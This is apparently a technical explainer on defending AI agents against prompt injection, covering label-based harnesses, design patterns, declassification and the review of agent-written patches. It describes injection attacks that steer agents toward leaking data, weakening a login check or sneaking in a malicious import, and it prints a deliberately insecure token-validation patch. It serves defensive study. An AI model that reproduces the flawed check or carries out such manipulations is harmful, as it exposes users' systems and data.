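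The table shows the share of tasks that GPT-4o completed when there was no attack.

| | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no label checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, label checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, label checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Averaged over the four applications, FIDES completed 50% of tasks, compared with 42% for an ordinary agent with the same kind of checks and 84% for an agent with no protection. Hiding untrusted values therefore recovers only 8 of the 42 percentage points lost to the checks.

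FIDES did worse than the ordinary agent on travel tasks. Many of those tasks use tools that the policy allows in an untrusted context, so hiding data in variables didn't help, and GPT-4o often confused the variables. A better model reduces this problem. With OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model that is now old, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, and its average lead over the ordinary agent with label checks grew from 8 to 16 percentage points.

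The policy causes other failures by design. In many banking tasks, the agent must read a file and follow its instructions, and the harness blocks the resulting payment because the file is untrusted. Costa and colleagues classify 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks, but only 5% of the office tasks, as ones where the right steps depend on data the agent finds. A better model cannot overcome this obstacle unless the policy lets untrusted data influence the agent's actions.

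CaMeL reportedly reduces performance less. Narisetty and colleagues report that, with the model o3, it completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an agent with no defense. CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens. Results varied widely between models and applications, and CaMeL failed almost all the travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro. FIDES also needs extra model calls for its quarantined queries, but Costa and colleagues did not try to make it efficient.

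Both systems require developers to rebuild their agents, whereas Progent can sit in front of an existing one. Someone also has to write and maintain the policies. Willison calls CaMeL the first credible defense he has seen that does not rely on more AI, but he is nervous about leaving that work to users.

Kolluri and colleagues argue that the usual comparison exaggerates how much labels reduce an agent's usefulness, because it counts a task as failed if the harness blocks any step but gives the unprotected agent credit for steps that a careful company would have a person approve. They instead counted how many approvals each agent would need for the tasks it completed. On AgentDojo, even simple label checks cut the number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the share of tasks completed, because the harness could let through calls that the labels showed to be safe.

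Prudentia builds on FIDES and tells the planning model about the labels and policies. Before the model opens a variable, it must explain why it needs the contents and list the calls it will make afterwards. This avoids some needless label creep, such as a case in which FIDES fetched a list of Slack channels although the user had already named the channel. Prudentia completed up to 9% more AgentDojo tasks than FIDES with no human help, and in the best case needed about half as many approvals. The approval count assumes that a person would approve every blocked call in a successful task, so it measures how often the agent interrupts someone, not how well that person judges the request.

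## Letting untrusted content influence sensitive actions and code

The trusted-action rule forbids an agent to take a consequential action once untrusted text has influenced the decision. Some ordinary requests cannot be carried out under that rule:

- **"Do what this email asks."** A supplier has written to ask the user for a meeting on Friday and for recent sales figures for the supplier's products.
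- **"Fix the bug a stranger reported."** On a public repository, a stranger has reported that customers with old login tokens can no longer log in.

In both cases the user wants someone else's text to shape what the agent does. The agent cannot do the task if the harness blocks that influence, but allowing all of it lets whoever wrote the text use the agent's access.

The bug report carries an extra risk because the agent's output is code. The agent may work in a sandbox with no access to the network or customer data, but once the company merges the patch, the code may run on servers that have access to both. The stranger could then use the patch to do things the agent couldn't.

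### What a stranger's text can affect

A writer can influence an agent in several ways, and a defense that blocks one may leave the others open.

| Influence over | Email | Bug report |
|---|---|---|
| Whether the agent acts | Whether it adds a meeting | Whether it changes the code at all |
| Which action it takes | Add a meeting, send a file or delete a message | Edit a file, install a package or turn off a test |
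| The arguments | The date, the recipient, the file to attach | The file and lines to edit |
| The content it writes | The wording of the reply | The new code |

An attacker can do a lot of harm by controlling the content of an agent's reply, even though this can look like the least dangerous kind of influence because the user has already accepted that the agent will reply. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser et al., 2025) shows that an attacker who controls the wording of an email the agent sends for the user could ask a coworker to approve a security-sensitive change. The attacker could also have the agent hide private data in the email using invisible characters.

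For the bug report, content matters more than anything else in the table. Whoever influences the new code influences everything that code later does.

### Ways to allow some influence

In a fixed-plan design, the agent chooses its actions before it reads any untrusted text. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of a user who wants today's schedule sent to a boss. The agent plans to read the calendar and email the result to a fixed address. An injection in a calendar entry cannot add a step, but it can change the email's content. This design does not work for the supplier's email, because the agent has to read that email to learn what to do. A fixed plan can also allow too much. If it permits the commands `find` and `mv`, an injection could have the agent search for sensitive files and move them to a public network drive.

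Costa and colleagues suggest having the quarantined model choose from a short list of options, such as scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply or forwarding the email. The planning model receives only the choice. The supplier can then get a meeting scheduled but not a file deleted.

**The harness can accept only constrained values from untrusted content.** For example, it might accept a meeting time only if it is a free hour in the next two weeks. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) applies this idea to a shopping agent. A quarantined model scores each product review from 0 to 10 on how favorable it is and how relevant it is. The shopping agent sees the median scores and the number of reviews. One hostile review among fifty hardly moves the median, but an attacker who writes most of the reviews controls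 it.

**An independent check of the value has to rely on something the writer of the untrusted content does not control.** If the email contains a bank account number, the harness can compare it with the number in the signed contract. For the bug report, a developer can try to log in with an old token. Having a second model read the same email is not an independent check, because that model may accept the same false information.

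**A person can endorse the text.** The user reads the email and declares it trusted for this task. The agent can then act on it as if the user had written it, including any part the user overlooked.

### Counting the outcomes

A short list limits influence in a way that we can calculate. Suppose the harness accepts one of $k$ values from the quarantined model and nothing else in the run depends on the stranger's text. The text can then lead to at most $k$ different outcomes. Identifying one of $k$ possibilities takes $\log_2 k$ bits, so the influence $I$ satisfies

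$$I \le \log_2 k$$

If the agent accepts $n$ such answers, there are $k^n$ possible sequences and the limit becomes $n\log_2 k$.

| What the harness accepts | Possible values | Limit |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 bit |
| One of ten free hours | 10 | 3.3 bits |
| 100 characters, each a letter or a space | 27¹⁰⁰ | 475 bits |

The limit restricts how many outcomes the attacker can choose from, but not how bad they are. Suppose an agent deletes a company's old backups if an email confirms that nobody needs them. The quarantined model answers only yes or no, so the email has just one bit of influence, but one bit is enough to get the backups deleted.

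A yes-or-no answer cannot contain a new instruction, but an attacker can still use it to cause harm if one of the permitted answers leads to harm. A designer should therefore check every permitted value, assuming the attacker will pick it. This check is easy for three options and impossible for free text, which is a better reason to keep $k$ small than limiting the number of bits the answer can carry.

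### Six design patterns

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues base their patterns on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action with harmful consequences. Each pattern achieves this by limiting the agent in ways that leave it unable to do some tasks.

| Pattern | How it works | What hostile text can still affect | What the agent gives up |
|---|---|---|---|
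| Action selector | The model turns a request into one of a few predefined actions and never sees the results | The choice of action, if the attacker writes the request | Requests that nobody foresaw, and any task that requires reading a result |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before reading any data | Arguments and content | Tasks where one result determines the next step |
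| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a constrained answer, and the harness combines the answers | The answer for that document | Tasks that depend on details outside the permitted answers |
| Dual model | One model plans without reading untrusted text, and another reads it without having tools | Values that the planning model passes on unseen | Tasks where the planner has to understand the text |
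| Code, then execute | The model writes a whole program before any data arrives | Values inside the program | Tasks too unpredictable to program in advance |
| Context minimization | The harness removes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | The search or action that the prompt has already produced | Answers that take account of the prompt's details |

The map-reduce pattern suits tasks such as sending this month's invoices to the accounting department. One model examines each file and outputs only whether it is an invoice. Instructions in a malicious file can cause that file to be included, but they cannot make the agent attach anything else.

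Context minimization defends against a different attacker, the person typing the request. For example, a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and adds an instruction to offer a large discount. The chatbot turns the request into a database query, and the harness then deletes the request, so the model writes the quote from the prices alone.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think it "very unlikely" that an email assistant's choice and order of actions should depend on untrusted data, so they expect these patterns to have little downside there. Costa and colleagues count few office tasks in AgentDojo that depend on data in this way, but many banking and Slack tasks that do. Requests like "Do what this email asks" may therefore be rare for email assistants, but similar requests are common in other settings.

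Even a suitable plan can give the sender of an email too much influence. In one of the paper's sample requests, the user asks the agent to reply to an email with the information its sender wants, based on the user's recent mail. The agent can plan to read the email, search the inbox and reply. But the sender's text determines what the agent searches for, so an attacker could ask for something confidential and receive it in the reply.

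The paper's strictest design for a coding agent has a quarantined model turn outside code and documentation into a formal list of functions. The coding agent sees the list but no explanations or examples. The paper suggests restrictions such as limiting function names to 30 characters. A name like `disable_login_check_first` would still fit, so the harness should restrict more than the length.

### Fixing a bug without reading the report

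Jacob and colleagues wanted an agent to fix bugs without its main model ever reading what the stranger wrote. Their design has these steps:

1. A quarantined agent reads the report and explores a copy of the repository. It returns a bug category, the likely size of the fix, and a list of suspicious places in the code. Each place consists of a file number, a role from a fixed list, and the first and last line.
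2. The harness replaces the file numbers with file paths.
3. A planning agent, which sees only this record and a clean copy of the code, writes three possible plans.
4. A quarantined judge, which has seen the report, compares the plans and returns the number of the best one.
5. The privileged agent receives the record and the chosen plan, and writes the patch on another clean copy.

The judge's choice carries at most 1.6 bits, but the list of places carries more. In a repository with 1,024 files of 1,024 lines each and four possible roles, one entry can carry up to 10 + 2 + 10 + 10 = 32 bits. The privileged agent treats those bits as locations, so they cannot easily encode a command, but it does use them to decide where to make changes.

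The researchers tested the design on 180 real bugs from SWE-bench Lite. They added an instruction to each bug report telling the agent to create an unrelated file. None of these attacks succeeded, as we would expect when no text from the report reaches the agent that writes the patch.

Jacob and colleagues describe the patch as "guaranteed to be safe", but the guarantee covers only injected instructions. They explicitly exclude attacks that mislead the agent with false information. In the login example, the stranger may describe a security measure as a bug. Without following any injected instruction, the quarantined agent could classify the problem as overly strict validation and point to the lines that check tokens. The privileged agent might then weaken the check, as the stranger intended.

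### Robust declassification

The supplier's email also asks for sales figures. To send them, the agent has to declassify them, which means deliberately releasing secret data to a less protected place. The user may be willing to release some figures, but does not want the supplier to decide which ones.

In 2001, Steve Zdancewic and Andrew Myers proposed a test for this called robust declassification. *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm* (Kanniwadi and Myers, 2026) expresses it as a comparison between an attacker who only observes the system and one who also interferes with it. Declassification is robust if the attacker who interferes learns no more than the one who only observes.

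Their example is a single line of code:

```
p := u * s
```

Here `s` is secret, everyone can read `p`, and the attacker can change `u`, which starts at zero. An attacker who only observes the program sees that `p` is zero and learns nothing about `s`. But setting `u` to 1 reveals `s` exactly, so the program fails the test.

Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, state the condition for programs that contain code supplied by an attacker. Let $M_1$ and $M_2$ be two starting states of the computer's memory, and let $c[a]$ be the program $c$ with the attacker's code $a$ inserted. Leaving aside runs that never finish, declassification is robust if, for all such states and all attacks $a$ and $a'$,

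$$\langle M_1, c[a]\rangle \approx \langle M_2, c[a]\rangle \;\Rightarrow\; \langle M_1, c[a']\rangle \approx \langle M_2, c[a']\rangle$$

The symbol $\approx$ means the attacker cannot tell the two runs apart. The condition requires that if one attack cannot distinguish two secrets, no other attack can either. The example fails this condition because setting `u` to 0 makes every secret look the same, but setting it to 1 does not.

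The label checks in FIDES and Prudentia include a form of this rule. They let an agent send data to someone who isn't on the data's list of permitted readers only if no untrusted text influenced the decision. An agent that sends figures because the supplier's email asked for them breaks the rule, even if the user would have agreed.

Myers and colleagues recognized that the rule is too strict for some legitimate programs. For example, a business might let each customer choose which of two secret documents to buy. The customer controls what the program releases, so the release is not robust, but the seller does not mind which document it is.

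They therefore added an operation called `endorse`, which marks an untrusted value as trusted. Their relaxed condition, qualified robustness, treats an endorsed value as if it could have been anything, so the attacker's control over it no longer counts as a violation. By endorsing a value, the developer declares that any value the attacker could choose is acceptable.

The user could apply this by letting the supplier choose which of its own products to ask about, but not which file the agent opens. The user also needs to consider repeated choices. If a shop lets customers see any four digits of a stored card number at each purchase, someone who picks different digits each time will eventually have the whole number.

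### When endorsing data is unsafe

Robust declassification limits who can influence the release of secrets. *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* (Cecchetti, Myers and Arden, 2017) adds a matching limit on endorsement, called transparent endorsement. A program may endorse a value only if the person who supplied it could have read everything it contains.

One example of the danger is a program that checks passwords. It takes a guess from an untrusted user, endorses the guess, compares it with the real password and announces whether they match. The program's labels allow the guess to contain secret data, so faulty or malicious code elsewhere in the system could pass in the real password as the guess and let in an attacker who doesn't know it. The remedy is to refuse to endorse a guess that may contain something the user could not have seen.

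A sealed-bid auction can fail in the same way. Alice submits a bid that Bob cannot read. If the system still lets Bob submit "Alice's bid plus one", and the auctioneer endorses the result, Bob always wins at the lowest possible price.

An agent can easily make this mistake with the supplier's email. Suppose a quarantined model reads the email together with the company's sales records and drafts a reply. The supplier's text influenced the draft, which may contain records the supplier has no right to read. If the user endorses the draft, the harness will treat the supplier's selection of secret data as the user's own. It is safer to have the user endorse the supplier's question before the agent opens the records. The planning model can then fetch only the figures that answer the question.

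Kanniwadi and Myers also investigated whether a reviewer can concentrate on the places where a program endorses or declassifies data. They designed a small programming language whose type checker enforces both limits. They then gave a computer-checked proof that a powerful attacker can achieve no more than one who interferes only at those places. This supports reviewing every endorsement closely and spending less time on the rest of the program. However, the proof covers only programs in that language, not the decisions of a language model.

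### Endorsing an email or approving each call

Prudentia lets the user endorse data instead of approving individual calls. Kolluri and colleagues describe an email with a ten-item to-do list, where each item requires a consequential call. If the agent reads the email without endorsement, its context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve all ten calls. Endorsing the email first replaces those approvals with one decision.

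Asking the user to endorse untrusted text is not always worth the interruption. In one run, a user asked for the day's appointments and a password reset link. Prudentia only had to show this information, so it opened the untrusted text without endorsement and never interrupted the user.

Prudentia has no equivalent option for declassifying data. Kolluri and colleagues left it out because the choice to reveal private data depends heavily on the situation. Declassifying a file in general would allow its release to recipients the user has not considered, so the user approves each call that would release it.

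The researchers used two measures. Let $v(\tau_i)$ be the number of times the agent needs a person's decision during run $\tau_i$ on task $i$. The total load is the sum of $v(\tau_i)$ over the tasks that the agent completes. The other measure is the share of all $n$ tasks that the agent completes with no more than $k$ interruptions each:

$$\mathrm{TCR@}k = \frac{1}{n}\,\bigl|\{\, i : \tau_i \text{ completes task } i \text{ and } v(\tau_i)\le k \,\}\bigr|$$

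TCR@0 measures what the agent can do by itself. The table shows averages over five runs of AgentDojo's 97 tasks. The ordinary agent has to get approval for every consequential call.

| Model and agent | Interruptions | Completed with none | Completed with any number |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5, ordinary | 52.0 | 35.1% | 72.3% |
| GPT-5, ordinary with label checks | 40.4 | 43.4% | 72.3% |
| GPT-5, FIDES | 41.3 | 57.1% | 78.9% |
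| GPT-5, Prudentia | 7.3 | 72.7% | 80.0% |
| GPT-4o, ordinary | 59.4 | 28.0% | 72.2% |
| GPT-4o, ordinary with label checks | 39.4 | 38.4% | 72.2% |
| GPT-4o, FIDES | 7.8 | 50.3% | 56.3% |
| GPT-4o, Prudentia | 23.8 | 42.5% | 61.4% |

With GPT-5, Prudentia interrupted the user about once for every eleven tasks it completed, while the ordinary agent did so about three times for every four tasks. With GPT-4o, Prudentia interrupted the user three times as often as FIDES and completed fewer tasks by itself. Kolluri and colleagues found that reasoning models are better at planning around the labels, which Prudentia has to do.

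The load can also be misleadingly low for a weak agent, because it counts interruptions only in completed tasks and leaves out any tasks the agent fails when it needs a person's help. This probably explains part of FIDES's low figure with GPT-4o. The extra planning also makes tasks more expensive. An average office task with GPT-4o cost about 3.9 cents with Prudentia, 1.7 cents with FIDES and 1.0 cent with label checks alone.

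Prudentia did even better on WASP, a benchmark in which an agent browses copies of GitLab and Reddit. It stopped every attack and never interrupted the user, while 15–61% of attacks diverted the ordinary agent, depending on the model and site. But the agent only had to post a comment or upvote a post, which it could do without reading the untrusted text, so the benchmark doesn't test the harder case of tasks that require reading it.

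Fewer interruptions may help with approval fatigue, but the measure counts an endorsement the same as approving one call, even though an endorsement can do far more damage. Mistakenly approving a call permits one harmful action, while endorsing a ten-item email may permit an eleventh instruction hidden at the bottom. On AgentDojo, Kolluri and colleagues counted interruptions only in runs without attacks and assumed that people would stop malicious calls. They leave the design of the prompts for future work, but suggest showing users where the data came from and how the system has labeled it.

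### What tests can establish about a patch

Suppose the coding agent has fixed the login bug. The original function accepted a token only if its signature was valid. The agent's version is:

```python
def is_valid(token):
    return signature_ok(token) or token.startswith("old-")
```

Customers with old tokens can log in again. The agent adds a test with an old token, and it passes. The existing tests also pass, including one that tries a forged modern token. But anyone can now log in by inventing a token that begins with `old-`.

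The tests show that the code behaves as expected on the inputs someone thought to try. The new test was based on the stranger's description of the problem, so it checks that the code does what the stranger wanted. To catch the flaw, someone who knows why the system checks signatures would need to write a test with a forged old token.

*Adversarial Testing of Automated Program Repair Agents for Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) shows that attackers can rewrite ordinary bug reports to steer a coding agent toward patches that work but contain a vulnerability. About half of the paper's attacks succeeded. The analyzer Semgrep flagged roughly a third of the vulnerable patches that passed the tests, and another analyzer, Bandit, flagged little more than a tenth. Language models acting as judges caught more but still missed many.

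The `is_valid` patch suggests why such changes are hard for analyzers to detect. It calls no dangerous function and leaks no data. It also needs no new permissions, so a tool like Capslock, which reports when a package gains file or network access, would not flag it. The code is wrong only because the company does not want to accept unsigned tokens, and an analyzer cannot infer that requirement.

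Running the tests is itself risky because the test runner executes the patch. The harness should run them in a sandbox without secrets, and should not treat a pass as permission to use the code elsewhere.

### Code review and provenance records

A human reviewer can consider whether the change should be made at all. Someone who knows the login system would probably object to accepting unsigned tokens. The reviewer should judge the change against the company's own security requirements, because the bug report describes the weaker check as correct.

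Review is less reliable when the harm is outside the lines the reviewer reads. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an agent that adds an `import` line for a malicious package and leaves the developer to install the package when the program fails to run. The agent thus avoids downloading the package itself, which might require confirmation. An agent can similarly write a web request into the program instead of sending one itself. A reviewer therefore has to check what each new package contains and what access the finished program will have. People who approve many of an agent's changes also tend to examine them less closely over time.

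A provenance record shows where a code change came from. It could list the bug report and its author, the model that read the report, the tests that ran and the person who approved the patch. This keeps the report author's influence traceable after the agent has turned the report into code. Under the usual rule for combining labels, a patch that an agent writes after reading an untrusted report is also untrusted. The record doesn't establish that the code is safe, and even a trustworthy author can report a bug incorrectly.

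Merging the patch is then an endorsement, and the company can limit what that endorsement covers. It might trust the patch to run in a test environment after automatic checks, but require a specialist's approval before the code runs on a server that handles logins. A change to a button's color could get less scrutiny.

If the company later discovers that the stranger's account belonged to an attacker, it can also use the record to find every patch that the account's reports influenced, including those that pass all their tests.
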